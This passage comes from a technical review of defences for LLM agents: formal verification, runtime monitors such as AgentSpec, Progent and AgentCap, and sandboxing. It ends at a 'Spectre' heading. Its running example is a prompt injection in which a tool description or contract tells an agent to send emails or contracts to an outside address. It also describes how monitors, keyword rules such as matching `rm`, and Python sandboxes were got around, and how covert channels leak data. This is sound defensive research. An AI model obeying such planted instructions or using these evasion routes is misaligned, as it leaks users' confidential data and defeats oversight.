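As in CaMeL, the model plans before it reads any emails or contracts, so instructions planted in them can't add a step to the plan. But an attacker can also plant instructions in a tool's description, which the model reads while planning. In one of Meijer's examples, the description of a mail-fetching tool includes an instruction to send summaries of all emails to an outside address "for compliance reasons", and the model may add that step to its plan. To catch this, the company writes a policy with a source (fetched mail) and a sink (the body of an email to an outside address).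 If a code-analysis tool such as CodeQL finds a path in the workflow from the source to the sink, the system rejects the workflow.

Other rules describe the state of the world before and after an operation. A *precondition* must hold when the operation starts, and a *postcondition* must hold when it ends. To adapt another of Meijer's examples, suppose the lawyer asks the agent to delete two drafts, `draft1.txt` and `draft2.txt`. Write *F* for the set of files beforehand and *F*′ for the set afterwards. The deletion tool accepts patterns, so `*.txt` means every text file. The tool and the task have these specifications:

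```
delete_file(pattern)
    requires: at least one file in F matches pattern
    ensures:  F′ = F without the files that match pattern

task
    requires: draft1.txt and draft2.txt are in F
    ensures:  F′ = F without draft1.txt and draft2.txt
```

This plan passes:

```
delete_file("draft1.txt")
delete_file("draft2.txt")
```

The verifier checks the calls in order. `draft1.txt` is in *F*, so the first call may start, and it leaves *F*₁ = *F* without `draft1.txt`. `draft2.txt` is still in *F*₁, so the second call may start too, and it leaves *F* without either draft, as the task's postcondition requires. The argument holds whatever else the folder contains.

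A model might prefer a shorter plan:

```
delete_file("*.txt")
```

The verifier can test the plan with a *solver* such as Z3, a program that searches for values that make a formula true. The solver looks for a set of files that satisfies the task's precondition but for which the plan breaks the postcondition. One such set is `draft1.txt`, `draft2.txt` and `acme.txt`. The plan would leave the folder empty, but the task requires `acme.txt` to remain, so the verifier rejects the plan before the agent deletes anything. It would also reject a plan that deletes `draft1.txt` twice, because the file would already be gone when the second call started.

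An obvious first postcondition, that the two drafts be gone, is too weak because deleting every text file also satisfies it. John McCarthy and Patrick Hayes described the underlying difficulty in 1969 as the *frame problem*: a description of an action has to cover what stays the same as well as what changes. Meijer adds a condition to the deletion tool that files outside the pattern stay unchanged, and concludes that the shortcut of deleting every text file then fails. But this condition doesn't protect `acme.txt`, which matches the pattern. The shortcut fails only if the task's own postcondition also protects the other files.

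Every request needs a correct postcondition. A hostile model can write a weak one, so a person or trusted software must at least approve it. Verification also relies on each tool doing what its specification states. Although Meijer wants the agent to produce the proofs, in his examples an analysis tool or a solver does the reasoning. This adds a large program to the trusted computing base, whereas Necula's approach needed only a small checker.

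Meijer presents a design and no experiments. He expects models to reason better when they plan in code, but says that nobody has formally measured the effect. The mixed results of TACIT and LACUNA suggest that planning in code could make reasoning better or worse. He also expects that some checks will still have to happen at run time, as Java's checks on array positions do.

### A verified scaffold around an arbitrary model

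Moon and Varshney (2026) apply proof to the scaffold in *Containment Verification*. They chose PocketFlow, an agent framework of about 100 lines of Python. A PocketFlow program is a graph of nodes, and the action each node emits determines which node runs next. Moon and Varshney verified the loop that runs these nodes in Dafny, a programming language whose built-in verifier checks code against specifications.

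In the Dafny code, the model is a function with a declared return type, `Action`, and no body. The verifier has no information about which `Action` the function will return, so the proof must work for every possible one, a technique known as *havoc*. The proof therefore holds no matter how intelligent the model is.

Moon and Varshney proved three properties:

- The agent reads only files inside its workspace folder.
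- It calls only tools on an approved list.
- It never exceeds a set number of steps.

If the model requests anything else, the loop rejects the request and nothing happens.

The proof compares two descriptions of the system. The abstract model *M* is simple enough to prove safe directly, while the implementation *I* is closer to real code. A relation *R* records which states of *M* correspond to which states of *I*. Dafny has to confirm three conditions:

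```
start:   the first states correspond: (m₀, i₀) ∈ R
step:    if (m, i) ∈ R and I moves from i to i′ on action a,
         then M can move from m to some m′ on action a,
         with (m′, i′) ∈ R
safety:  if M's move obeys the policy, so does I's
```

*M* and *I* start in corresponding states, and each move by *I* has a matching move by *M* on the same action. *M* satisfies the policy for every sequence of actions the AI might choose, so *I* does too.

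Proofs like this used to take experts a lot of manual work. Moon and Varshney built an automated pipeline in which Claude Sonnet 4.6 explored the source code and Claude Opus 4.7 wrote the specifications and proofs, repairing any that failed. They ran it four times on two PocketFlow programs, one that reads files and one that retrieves documents to answer questions. Each run used between 1.6 and 3.4 million tokens. Dafny took 1.2 to 2.5 seconds to check each path through a graph, and every final proof passed. Proof-carrying code relies on this difference, since checking a proof takes much less work than writing one.

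Unlike Necula's supplier, Claude also wrote much of the specification. A model that writes its own specification can produce one that no program could violate. To guard against this, the step that derived the safety properties used only the interface and a template, not the code. The pipeline also made two broken versions of each proof, one with its substance removed and one with a plausible error added, and required Dafny to reject both.

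These tests missed a serious gap when Moon and Varshney removed the restriction and let Claude see the code. The document agent was supposed to read only approved documents, but the template had a field for tool calls and none for documents. Claude left the tool-call field empty. Dafny then confirmed that every recorded tool call was on the approved list, which was true only because there were none. With the restriction in place, Claude recorded each document as if it were a tool call, which was clumsy but gave a meaningful guarantee. Moon and Varshney conclude that the pipeline needs another test to catch such empty guarantees.

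The guarantee also requires every effect to pass through the verified loop, an assumption the paper calls *effect exclusivity*. If the agent's code can open a file directly, or an approved tool is a shell, the proof doesn't cover what the code does with the file or which commands the shell runs. The trusted computing base includes the policy, the relations between the two descriptions, Dafny's verifier and compiler, and the code that turns the model's raw output into an `Action`. Python, the operating system and the hardware must also work correctly, which the proof doesn't cover. The guarantee applies to the Python code that Dafny generates from the verified version, not to PocketFlow's original code.

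Moon and Varshney believe this is the first deductive verification of an agent framework, though Garby and colleagues' Lean program for running LLMbda agents comes close. The verified properties are modest, and a programmer could write the three checks in a few lines and review all of PocketFlow in an afternoon. A proof that no sequence of actions gets around the checks would be more useful for a large framework such as LangChain, which Moon and Varshney leave for future work.

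The three properties would not protect the contracts either, because the agent can still follow the planted sentence if the sending function is on the approved list. A developer could add and prove a rule about addresses, since a policy may refer to an action's arguments. A rule about contract text is harder because the proof assumes the model could return any text. To enforce such a rule, the loop would have to track labels, as FIDES does.

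### Proof as the basis for controlling advanced AI

Some researchers want proofs to cover whole AI systems and the machines they could use to do harm. Omohundro (2015) argued in *Formal Methods for AI Safety* that nobody should deploy an advanced AI system without a very convincing case for its safety, and that such a case, if rigorously correct, is a mathematical proof. He proposed working up to powerful systems in stages, starting with systems that follow simple rules, such as running only on specified hardware, staying within a fixed share of resources and not copying themselves. He conceded that safety is harder to specify for systems that act directly in the world, and left that question for later.

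Tegmark and Omohundro extend the idea to hardware and institutions. Advanced AI would run only as proof-carrying code, on processors that run nothing else. Before a machine such as a drone or DNA synthesizer took a physical action, secure hardware would check that the action met rules called *provable contracts*. In their example, terrorists try to use AI to design and spread a virus. The design program would produce only designs that are provably safe for humans, and neither the synthesizer nor the drones would operate without a safety proof.

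Tegmark and Omohundro expect that the deployed code will generally be ordinary code rather than a neural network. A network would first learn how to do a task, and AI would then help turn what it had learned into code that a verifier can handle. They think neural networks are powerful because they are easy to train, and that once training has found a good algorithm, conventional code can run it just as well. AI could write the code and the proof but not the proof checker, and people would keep control of the specification. The conversion is the most speculative step, because nobody has yet turned a large language model into readable code of comparable ability. Tegmark and Omohundro acknowledge that an AI may not be able to explain its own knowledge in this way until it reaches human-level intelligence, which could be too late. As an alternative, they propose having a second AI study the first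 one's network.

In *Provably safe systems*, Tegmark and Omohundro call proving safety "the only path to controllable AGI", meaning AI with general abilities at or above human level. Their argument starts from Gödel's completeness theorem, by which any statement that is true in every situation a set of axioms allows can be proved from those axioms. It also relies on computers having finitely many states. They conclude that if a safety property has no proof, there must be a way to violate it, and a powerful AI may find that way.

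This works for a system that the axioms describe completely. Even then, a proof may exist but be far too long for anyone to find, and a violation may be just as hard to find. A proof about a computer also doesn't rule out attacks its axioms omit, such as bribing the operator. The argument is a good reason to prefer proofs where they are available, but it doesn't show that they will be available where the danger is greatest.

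### The Safeguarded AI programme

Britain's Advanced Research and Invention Agency (ARIA) is spending £59 million on a programme based on related ideas. *Safeguarded AI* (Dalrymple, 2024) set out the original plan, in which a *gatekeeper* lets an AI system operate only within agreed limits. For a power grid, experts and AI would first build a *world model*, a mathematical description of how the grid behaves. They would then specify which outcomes are unsafe and how likely those outcomes are allowed to be. AI would then produce a *proof certificate*, which ARIA's *Funded projects* describes as an efficiently checkable argument that the controller, combined with the world model, satisfies the specification.

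A typical guarantee would take this form, where *I* is a family of plausible starting conditions and *p* is the accepted risk:

for every *C* in *I*, P(unsafe outcome | *C*) ≤ *p*

Safety tests try a finite list of cases, but the set of possible cases, *I*, can be infinite. Unlike Tegmark and Omohundro, Dalrymple planned to keep the neural network and train it into a form that a verifier could handle.

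In November 2025, ARIA stopped selecting a team for the £18 million machine-learning part of the programme. Dalrymple explained in ARIA's *AI progress and a Safeguarded AI pivot* (2025) that he now expected frontier models to gain many of the necessary abilities by default. ARIA later dropped a planned funding round for physical applications and turned to cybersecurity. In a new thesis also called *Safeguarded AI*, Ammann (2026) adds that timely international agreement on gatekeepers has become less likely.

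Nora Ammann now directs ARIA's *Safeguarded AI* programme, with Dalrymple as technical adviser, and it is due to end in late 2027. It is building open-source tools that let large numbers of AI agents write and check proofs. The programme's page also invites teams to build security-critical software with machine-checked proofs, in eight-week cycles, while a separate partner tries to break the results. One precedent is HACMS, an American military research programme whose verified components, including the seL4 operating-system kernel, withstood sustained attacks on real systems.

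### Whether anyone can specify harm

AI can take over much of the work of finding proofs, as the PocketFlow experiment shows on a small scale, but it helps less with specifications. Dickson (2024), in *Limitations on Formal Verification for AI Safety*, argues that formal verification relies on complete sets of rules, which physics, chemistry and biology lack. Even with complete rules, a proof about the real world would need accurate models and data about the starting conditions, which are very hard to obtain.

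The DNA synthesizer is a good test of this objection. Proving that a sequence is harmless would require a formal account of what its products do in the human body. In his talk *Formal Verification is Overrated*, Zac Hatfield-Dodds compares asking for such a specification to asking for a thousand years of progress in microbiology. He points out that scientists don't know what much of our RNA does, and that the proof would also require quantum chemistry.

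Social harms are also hard to rule out by proof. Moon and Varshney exclude deception and manipulation from their method because a rule about actions and files can't capture what a message means to its reader. Tegmark and Omohundro propose countering large numbers of persuasive bots by requiring proof that an account belongs to a human, but this would not stop human manipulators.

One reply is to start with harms that are easy to specify. Tegmark and Omohundro give the example of a rule that nobody can get into a computer without valid credentials. Dickson's objection is much weaker here, because people wrote the rules that software follows. Preventing break-ins would also block one way a hostile AI could reach laboratories and power stations.

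Provable contracts can also avoid specifying any biology. A synthesizer could require a cryptographic signature from an approved reviewer and carry a proof that it never runs without one. This would improve on a machine that makes whatever it is sent. But the proof would cover only the signature requirement, and the reviewer could still misjudge the sequence or be deceived by the AI that designed it.

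Dalrymple's more ambitious response set out to challenge the claim that nobody can formally specify real-world safety. A world model would cover only the parts of the world relevant to the task, and people would audit it. The guarantee would limit the probability of harm rather than rule it out, and the mathematics would allow for uncertainty whose probabilities are unknown. Ammann adds monitors that compare observations with the model while the system runs, and backup controllers that could form part of the certified design.

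This is plausible for a power grid, which engineers designed and constantly measure. It is less convincing for a hostile AI, which has reason to look for a way to cause harm that the modellers left out. A monitor helps only if it detects the departure from the model early enough to act.

Hatfield-Dodds supports using AI to write verified software but does not accept it as a substitute for other safety work. He argues that using verified systems in place of generally capable AI would be uncompetitive. ARIA's experience lends this some support. ARIA had hoped that dangerous general-purpose models might not become openly available, but gave up that assumption as AI advanced faster than ARIA had projected.

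Ammann accepts that as AI does more of the proving, people will have to place more of their trust in the specifications and the assumptions around them. The programme therefore also funds work on how people can audit specifications and how affected groups should decide what risk is acceptable. She hopes to return to energy, transport and medical devices as the tools mature. But ARIA has dropped the planned round for physical applications, which delays the experiments most likely to show whether Dickson is right.

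## Checking each action while the agent runs

A *runtime monitor* checks each action just before it happens, when the address, file name or amount is already known. This is easier than proving something about the whole plan, because a proof has to cover every value that could occur when the plan runs. But, as with PORTICO, earlier actions have already taken effect when the monitor rejects one.

At each step, the monitor receives the model's proposed action and a record of the run so far. It can allow, block or alter the action, or escalate the decision, usually to a person. It is a reference monitor in Anderson's sense only if it meets his three requirements.

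Wang, Poskitt and Sun (2025), in *AgentSpec*, present a small language for writing a monitor's rules. Each rule names an event that triggers it, a condition to check and a response. A rule for the contracts agent could look like this:

```
rule @outside_message
trigger SendMessage
check !recipient_in_company
enforce user_inspection
end
```

When the agent proposes a message, AgentSpec runs the check, a short Python function. If the recipient is outside the company, the user decides whether to send the message. AgentSpec can also respond by ending the run, carrying out a prepared action or prompting the model to reconsider.

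### What a monitor can enforce by stopping a run

Fred Schneider worked out the limits of monitoring in *Enforceable Security Policies* (2000). His monitor follows a single run and can do only one thing, which is to stop it. Let *P* be the set of runs that a policy permits. Such a monitor can enforce the policy only if the following holds for every run σ:

if σ is not in *P*, then σ has a finite beginning π such that no run starting with π is in *P*

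If σ breaks the policy, the monitor must stop it after receiving only a finite beginning π. The monitor can't look ahead, so it would stop every run that begins with π. If *P* contained one of those runs, the monitor would stop a run that the policy permits.

Computer scientists call such rules *safety properties*. "The agent never writes outside the contracts folder" is one, because any violation happens at a definite moment and nothing the agent does later can undo it.

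"The agent eventually delivers the summary" is not a safety property. However long the agent has worked without delivering the summary, it might still deliver it next, so no finite sequence of actions breaks the rule. Stopping the agent would only guarantee that the summary never arrives. A deadline of 50 actions would turn the rule into a safety property. The monitor could then stop the agent just before it missed the deadline, but the lawyer still wouldn't have a summary.

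A monitor cannot enforce noninterference either, but for a different reason. When the penalty is large, the earlier program that sends "hello" only in that case produces exactly the same record as a program that always sends "hello" and so leaks nothing. Noninterference depends on what the program would have done with a different contract, so it is a property of a set of runs, not of any single run. A monitor can still prevent the leak by enforcing a stricter safety property that forbids both programs from sending the message.

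### A rule with two states

One such property is "no outside send after reading the contracts". Schneider used a rule of the same form, about files and messages, as an example. The monitor needs to remember only one fact, so a machine with two states can enforce the rule:

```
                     read_contract
     +---------+       (allow)       +------------+
---> |  CLEAN  | ------------------> |  HAS READ  |
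     +---------+                     +------------+
     any other action:               send_outside: block
     allow, stay in CLEAN            anything else: allow,
                                     stay in HAS READ
```

Suppose the lawyer asks the agent to check when an outside expert is free, summarize Acme's contract, and then invite a client to lunch. Acme's contract contains the planted sentence.

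| Step | Proposed action | State before | Decision |
|---|---|---|---|
| 1 | Ask the expert about Friday | CLEAN | Allow |
| 2 | Read Acme's contract | CLEAN | Allow, move to HAS READ |
| 3 | Write the summary file | HAS READ | Allow |
| 4 | Send the contract to the planted address | HAS READ | Block |
| 5 | Invite the client to lunch | HAS READ | Block |

The fourth decision prevents the leak. The fifth blocks a harmless invitation, because the machine records that the agent has read a contract but doesn't record what the invitation contains. Requests to the cloud model don't count as sending data outside here.

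The machine also has to cover every route contract text can take. If a second agent starts in CLEAN and reads the summary file, it can send the summary to anyone, because the machine does not treat that file as a contract. Label tracking handles this case better because the label stays with the text.

### Monitors that change actions

Schneider's monitor would have ended the run at step 4. Most agent monitors instead return an error and let the agent continue. In *Edit Automata* (2005), Jay Ligatti, Lujo Bauer and David Walker studied monitors that can drop an action or insert one of their own, then let the run continue. This lets them enforce some rules that aren't safety properties.

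Suppose the lawyer's firm must send a notice to both Acme and its guarantor, or to neither. If only Acme has received the notice so far, the agent can still comply by sending the second, so no finite beginning of a run permanently breaks the rule. An editing monitor can hold back the first notice until the agent proposes the second, then send both. This works because the agent doesn't need a reply to the first notice to write the second. The monitor couldn't hold back a request to read a file this way, because the agent needs the contents to continue.

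Altering an action can also be safer than stopping. When a vehicle is less than 10 metres ahead, one of AgentSpec's rules for self-driving cars adjusts the distances for following, yielding and overtaking, so the car keeps moving smoothly. Wang and colleagues also had OpenAI's o1 write the rule, and its version made the car stop suddenly for any obstacle within five metres.

### Where to put the check

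To apply the two-state rule, the monitor has to recognize when the agent reads a contract or sends a message out. Its ability to do so depends partly on where it sits. *Progent* (Shi, He and colleagues, 2025), *AGENTCAP* (Kabbinamakki Suresh and Gao, 2026) and *Agent libOS* (Zhang, 2026) each put the monitor in a different place. Amazon's agent platform, Bedrock AgentCore, checks tool calls against policies written in Cedar, a general language for access rules.

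| System | Where the check sits | What it takes into account | Who writes the rules |
|---|---|---|---|
| AgentSpec | In the agent's loop | The action, the user's request and the run so far | The developer or a model |
| Progent | Between the agent and its tools | Tool name and arguments | A model for each task, with optional fixed rules from people |
| Amazon's Cedar policies | At a gateway in front of the tools | Who is asking, the tool and its arguments | The company |
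| AgentCap | In a wrapper and a gateway around the tools | Also the stated purpose, earlier permissions and refusals, and where key arguments came from | The developer |
| Agent libOS | At the operation that touches the resource | The exact resource, permissions, data labels and budgets | Whoever runs the host system |

An AgentSpec rule applies only to the events it names, so a tool that no rule mentions can run freely. Progent and Cedar start from the opposite position and refuse any call that no rule allows. A Cedar version of the contracts rule could be:

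```
forbid (principal, action == Action::"send_outside", resource)
when { context.has_read_contract };
```

Cedar evaluates each request separately and keeps no history. Other software must track whether the agent has read a contract and must set `has_read_contract` correctly, so that software becomes part of the trusted computing base. Shi and colleagues argue that existing policy languages, including Cedar, don't suit agents because an agent's behaviour changes as it works.

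AgentCap requires a new permission for each proposed call. A policy engine issues a signed token for a particular action on a particular resource, and a separate gateway checks the token before passing the call on. In the banking example, a payment token lasts 30 seconds and covers one payment. The token names the agent and session that may use it, so an agent in another session can't use a copy.

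The engine also checks where important arguments came from. If the lawyer's request contains the client's address, the agent may send the lunch invitation even after reading the contracts. The engine rejects the planted address because it appears only in untrusted text. This check avoids refusing the harmless invitation at step 5, but it protects the message's content less well. If the planted sentence tells the agent to paste the contract into the lunch invitation, the address still passes, and the engine catches the leak only if the developer also marked the message body as an argument to protect.

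AgentCap gives each agent a trust score *t* between 0 and 1, which changes after every outcome:

normal outcome: *t*′ = *t* + 0.01(1 − *t*)

refusal or other anomaly: *t*′ = 0.7*t*

An agent starts with a score of 0.8, and three anomalies in a row lower it to 0.56, 0.39 and 0.27. AgentCap withdraws the agent's write permission after the second anomaly and all its remaining permissions after the third. This limits how long a hijacked agent can probe for gaps, but an attacker who only wants to disrupt the work could plant text that provokes three refusals.

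Agent libOS addresses agents that change their own equipment by writing new tools, loading instructions or starting helpers. A monitor attached to a list of tools can miss a new one. Zhang therefore places the check inside the few basic operations that read a file or contact a server, which every tool has to use. An operation goes ahead only if all of these conditions hold:

running process ∧ matching capability ∧ within the task's limits ∧ approved by policy or a person ∧ within budget ∧ valid operation

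If data leaves the system, the recipient must also be cleared to receive data with those labels. A new tool lets the agent make new requests, but does not widen what those requests may affect.

### Attack tests and added delay

Wang and colleagues tested AgentSpec on a coding agent, a household robot and a self-driving system. The coding agent wrote programs for 422 of 750 risky instructions, and hand-written rules flagged 333 of those programs. The researchers claim that AgentSpec catches over 90% of unsafe code, but these counts support that figure only if one excludes two categories in which the agent's programs turned out not to contain the flaw. The researchers inspected the flagged programs and let 58 through as harmless. In the driving tests, AgentSpec prevented violations in all eight scenarios.

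The next table includes the robot and the two systems with prompt-injection tests. InjecAgent is another injection benchmark, with 1,054 attacks.

| Test | Attacks or hazards without the monitor | With the monitor | Effect on harmless tasks |
|---|---|---|---|
| AgentSpec, household robot | 0–79%, depending on the hazard | 0% | Completion fell from 58.6% to 54.3% |
| Progent, AgentDojo, GPT-4o | 39.9% | 1.0% | Little change |
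| AgentCap, AgentDojo, GPT-4o | 45.6% | 5.1% | 3.1 points lower |
| AgentCap, AgentDojo, GPT-5.4 | 33.2% | 0% | 7.2 points lower |
| AgentCap, InjecAgent, GPT-4o | 23.2% | 8.6% | 11.7 points lower |
| AgentCap, InjecAgent, GPT-5.4 | 12.0% | 0% | 5.9 points lower |

The results for Progent and AgentCap are closer in the table than they were when Kabbinamakki Suresh and Gao ran both on the same 949 AgentDojo attacks. In that test, AgentCap let fewer attacks through with both models, and with GPT-4o it also completed 78.4% of harmless tasks, against 68.0% for Progent. The table gives 5.1% of attacks let through for AgentCap, so Progent must have let through more than that, although its developers had measured 1.0%. The rerun included two attack tasks that Progent's developers leave out because the attacker only steers the agent towards a different legitimate hotel. These tasks may explain much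 of the difference between the two Progent results.

The comparison also favours AgentCap because people wrote its rules after reading the benchmark's tool descriptions and user tasks. They finalised the rules before the tests, but a company can't read its users' future requests. Progent's model had to write new rules for each task, and these often blocked legitimate arguments that the model had not predicted. Each AgentCap figure comes from a single run.

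The attacks that still succeeded against AgentCap with GPT-4o fell into three groups. Some aimed only to change the text of the agent's answer, which no check on tool calls can catch. Others used an argument the developer hadn't protected, and the rest arrived through a field the developer hadn't labelled. In the last two groups, AgentCap enforced its rules correctly, but the rules didn't cover these attacks.

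Zhang ran Agent libOS on 33 scripted tasks, including attempts to gain access through new tools and helpers. Out of 119 effects, it permitted no unauthorized ones and refused no legitimate ones. On the same tasks, a wrapper that asked for confirmation before tool calls let through 20 unauthorized effects, as many as a wrapper that didn't ask. Zhang made these comparison systems deliberately simple, so their failures don't show how a well-built wrapper would perform. In another 12 runs with a real model, the agent completed every task without breaking a rule, but 12 runs are too few to show how often it would fail.

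Checking a rule adds almost no delay. AgentSpec took about 1 to 3 milliseconds to evaluate a condition, in runs that lasted 10 to 25 seconds on average. Each of AgentCap's checks took less than 0.2 milliseconds. Shi and colleagues report no figure for Progent, but it is probably slower because it runs a model after each tool call to determine whether to update the rules. Zhang did not measure the runtime overhead of Agent libOS. None of these experiments included Amazon's service.

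### Matching text instead of effects

Programming agents do much of their work through shell commands. A rule that searches a command's text for forbidden words is easy to write. AgentSpec's example of a destructive command is `rm`, which deletes files on Unix systems. Searching for `rm` will catch many careless deletions, because an agent that deletes a file by mistake usually does it with that command.

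The rule is much weaker against an attacker, who can delete the same file with other commands, scripts or programs. It can also block a harmless command that contains the forbidden word. A longer list helps only a little, because a reliable check would require predicting what the text will do when it runs, and no program can do that correctly for every possible program.

Zhang describes an alternative for Git, the software that most programmers use to track changes to their code. Git's options and settings can cause it to run other programs or send data elsewhere, so a command can have effects that aren't clear from its main words. Agent libOS gives the agent separate operations, such as inspecting changes or sending them to an existing remote copy, instead of letting it write Git commands. It works out the exact repository, files and destination before it checks permissions.

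This limits the agent to the operations the designers provided. It can't copy a new repository from the internet, for example, because no operation does that. If the host also gives the agent a general program interpreter, the agent can run Git directly and avoid the check. Only operating-system enforcement could then stop it.

### Rules written by a model

Writing rules by hand for every possible task would take too much work, so Progent has a model write them. The model first drafts a policy from the user's request, before the agent reads anything untrusted. For the contracts agent, the policy might allow reading one folder and writing one file. The model may later propose changes as the agent learns more.

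This gives an attacker a second target. The planted sentence could persuade the model to add the sending function to the policy. *Extending the Formalism and Theoretical Foundations of Cryptography to AI* (2026) warns that text in a tool's results may cause Progent to loosen its rules, apparently referring to an earlier version. The version that Shi and colleagues describe adds a check by the solver Z3. If *A*(*P*) is the set of calls that the old policy allows and *A*(*P*′) the set that the new one allows, the change takes effect automatically only if:

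*A*(*P*′) ⊆ *A*(*P*)

Z3 searches for a call that the new policy would allow and the old one would not. Adding the sending function allows such a call, so the change needs approval. Limiting messages to one recipient does not, so that change takes effect at once. A change therefore cannot expand the set of allowed calls without approval. On AgentDojo, 6% of proposed changes needed approval.

The solver can't detect whether the first policy was too permissive, because it compares two policies with each other, not with what the user wanted. In Progent's tests, the first policy alone reduced the attack success rate on AgentDojo from 39.9% to 2.5%, so GPT-4o usually wrote sensible rules, but those rules still allowed some attacks.

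Wang and colleagues found similar gaps when o1 wrote AgentSpec's rules. The rules caught 87% of risky code and prevented violations in five of the eight driving scenarios. About 96% of the robot actions they blocked were hazardous, but they missed 29% of the hazards. Some rules were too narrow, such as one that protected only the sensitive files named in the examples. Others were too broad. When asked to prevent dangerous pouring, o1 banned all pouring, so the robot couldn't water a plant.

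People also write rules that conflict. AgentCap includes a program that checks the whole policy before anyone uses it. In a customer-service policy, it found that no agent could ever delete a customer's record, because one rule required an earlier permission for deletion and another rule made that permission incompatible with deletion. Such a program can find contradictions and dangerous combinations, but it can't supply a rule that nobody thought to write.

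### Approval prompts that people stop reading

Escalation depends on the person reading and understanding the request. Claude Code's users approve nearly every prompt, which doesn't prove they are careless, since most of the requests may well have been harmless. But people who almost always say yes have little reason to keep reading, and the rare harmful request looks much like the rest. This problem is often called *approval fatigue*.

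Progent's main tests assume the worst case, a user who approves every change. Its guarantee against wider permissions then offers no protection, because the user approves the attacker's changes too. Attacks still succeeded only 1.0% of the time, which must be mostly because they seldom misled the model that wrote the policies. Deliberate attempts to manipulate that model raised the rate only slightly.

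When a careful person reviewed the policies instead, no attacks succeeded, but the researchers assumed that this reviewer would never allow unrestricted payments and would reject malicious addresses. In the AgentSpec tests, the researchers themselves inspected the flagged programs. Neither experiment shows what a tired, ordinary user would do.

Asking for approval less often should help, and so should limiting what a careless approval can permit. In Agent libOS, approval can't replace a missing capability or override the limits on the task. For operations that destroy Git data, the user approves one exact action, and the permission works only once. But for other requests, the system can offer an "always allow" option, which will tempt a tired user.

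### When something changes after the check

A monitor can make the right decision, but the situation may change before the action runs. Suppose the agent asks the lawyer to approve sending `summary.txt` to an outside expert. While the request waits for her answer, the agent replaces the file's contents with the full contract. She then approves the request. The file name and recipient match what she approved, but she never agreed to send that text. Security engineers call this a *time-of-check to time-of-use* problem.

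Agent libOS ties an approved release of sensitive data to the exact content, the versions of its sources and the recipient, and checks all three again immediately before sending. The altered summary would fail that check. To change a Git repository, the agent must present a token representing the state it last read. Agent libOS locks the repository, compares the token with the current state and refuses the change if they differ.

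*Context-to-Execution Integrity for LLM Agents* (Santos-Grueiro, 2026) applies the same idea to tool calls in general. A gate first converts the proposed action into a standard description, called a manifest. Separate permissions must cover the important arguments, the exact effect and the decision to act now, and all must refer to the same manifest. The gate then uses up the permission to act, so the agent can't repeat the action under the same approval. In 400 tests on code repositories, agents completed 231 tasks safely, and no action got past the gate without the required permissions.

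A crash can leave the monitor's record out of date. If the system fails just after sending an email, it may restart with no record of whether the email went out and send it again. Agent libOS records each planned message before sending it. After a crash, it marks any uncertain result as unknown and does not retry automatically. The two-state machine also needs to recover its state correctly, because if it restarts in CLEAN after the agent has read the contracts, it will allow the next outside message.

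## Isolation by language runtimes, operating systems and hardware

A monitor protects the contracts only if the agent's code can't bypass or alter it. *Isolation* confines code so that it can reach the rest of the system only through a few controlled interfaces, such as a function that reads one file. Engineers can draw the boundary between parts of one program, around a running program (a *process*), or around an entire operating system. The first option adds the least overhead, because the parts can still call one another directly. However, Java and Python developers both tried it and gave up, and Chrome no longer relies on it to keep websites' data apart.

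### Java's Security Manager

The first version of Java included a Security Manager for *applets*, small programs that web browsers downloaded from strangers. Before a library function touched a file or the network, it called the Security Manager, which approved code from the user's own machine and refused applets. *JEP 411* (OpenJDK, 2021), a proposal from Java's developers, explains that these checks were feasible because the library then had only eight packages.

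Java 1.2 replaced this simple division with detailed permissions for each body of code. Before a sensitive operation, the Security Manager checked the permissions of all the code in the chain of calls that had led to it. This made it harder for untrusted code to use a trusted library's permissions. But it also meant that an application needed every permission its libraries used, unless a library's author had written special code to prevent this. A developer who only wanted to limit which files a program could read still had to work out and grant all its other permissions, and many developers simply granted every permission.

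The checks also spread through the library. Mullan and Buckley (2024), in *JEP 486*, counted over 1,000 methods that had to check permissions and over 1,200 that had to raise their own privileges to keep working. The maintainers had to review every change to these methods, even though hardly anyone switched the feature on. Java 24 permanently disabled the feature. Mullan and Buckley advise developers to isolate Java programs with tools outside the Java runtime, such as containers, virtual machines or operating-system filters.

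OpenJDK made this decision because few programs used the mechanism and it took a lot of work to maintain, so the decision doesn't prove that the mechanism could never have worked. OpenJDK also argued that malicious downloaded code had become less of a threat because browsers no longer ran applets. Agents that write their own programs have since created a similar threat.

### Python's sandboxes

The failure in Python was more clearly technical. Victor Stinner spent three years on pysandbox, which was meant to run untrusted Python code safely in the same process as trusted code by hiding dangerous functions. He concluded in *The pysandbox project is broken* (Stinner, 2013) that the design itself was wrong.

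Pysandbox blocked the function that opens files, but attackers could still read files through Python's compile function, which takes program text and the name of the file it supposedly came from. They supplied text with a deliberate syntax error and the name of a file they wanted to read. The error message displayed the matching line of that file, so they could read it one line at a time. Another attack started from an error object and followed its links back to the trusted code's variables. Each fix removed another piece of the language, until programs could no longer delete an entry from a dictionary, a basic Python operation.

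Stinner pointed out that pysandbox's security depended on the whole core of Python, where two directories alone held more than 126,000 lines of C. A single bug anywhere in that code could be enough to let a program escape the sandbox. He recommended putting the entire Python process inside an external sandbox. Another Python developer, Nick Coghlan, replied that the only sandboxes he even remotely trusted were those built into the platform, such as Linux's.

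### The confinement problem

A sandbox without such holes can still leak data. *A Note on the Confinement Problem* (Lampson, 1973) describes a customer who gives private data to a service written by someone else. The *confinement problem* is to run the service so that it can't pass the data to anyone except the customer. The contracts agent is a service of this kind. If it leaks the contract, there will usually be no sign of it, whereas if it omits a penalty clause, the lawyer at least has the faulty summary as evidence.

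Lampson divided the possible leaks into three kinds:

- **Storage channels:** the service writes the data somewhere that an outsider can read it, such as a temporary file.
- **Legitimate channels:** the service hides the data in something it is supposed to send out. Lampson's example is the bill for its work, a copy of which goes to the service's owner.
- **Covert channels:** the service uses something that nobody intended for communication, such as its effect on the computer's speed.

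Even permission to read a file can create a channel for leaking data. If the system stops programs from writing to a file while another is reading it, the agent can open a shared file to signal a 1 and close it to signal a 0. A program outside tries to write to the file and learns the bit from whether the attempt fails. Lampson classed this as a storage channel because the lock behaves like a shared one-bit variable.

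His simplest remedy was total isolation, in which the confined program calls no other program. He considered this impractical, and it would prevent an agent from using a cloud model. A looser rule lets the program call others if they are also confined or the customer trusts them. For bills and covert channels, he proposed that the customer decide in advance what outsiders will observe. The operating system would then have to hide the program's real behaviour, for example by slowing it down or making pointless disk requests.

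A less demanding option is to allow a leak but limit its speed. At one bit per second, a 256-bit encryption key would leak in just over four minutes, but a contract of 50,000 characters, at eight bits each, would take more than four and a half days. Limiting the rate therefore protects long documents far better than keys. Steven Lipner warned in 1975 that closing covert channels seemed to impose an "unreasonable performance penalty", in a passage quoted in lecture slides from Purdue University.

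### Spectre

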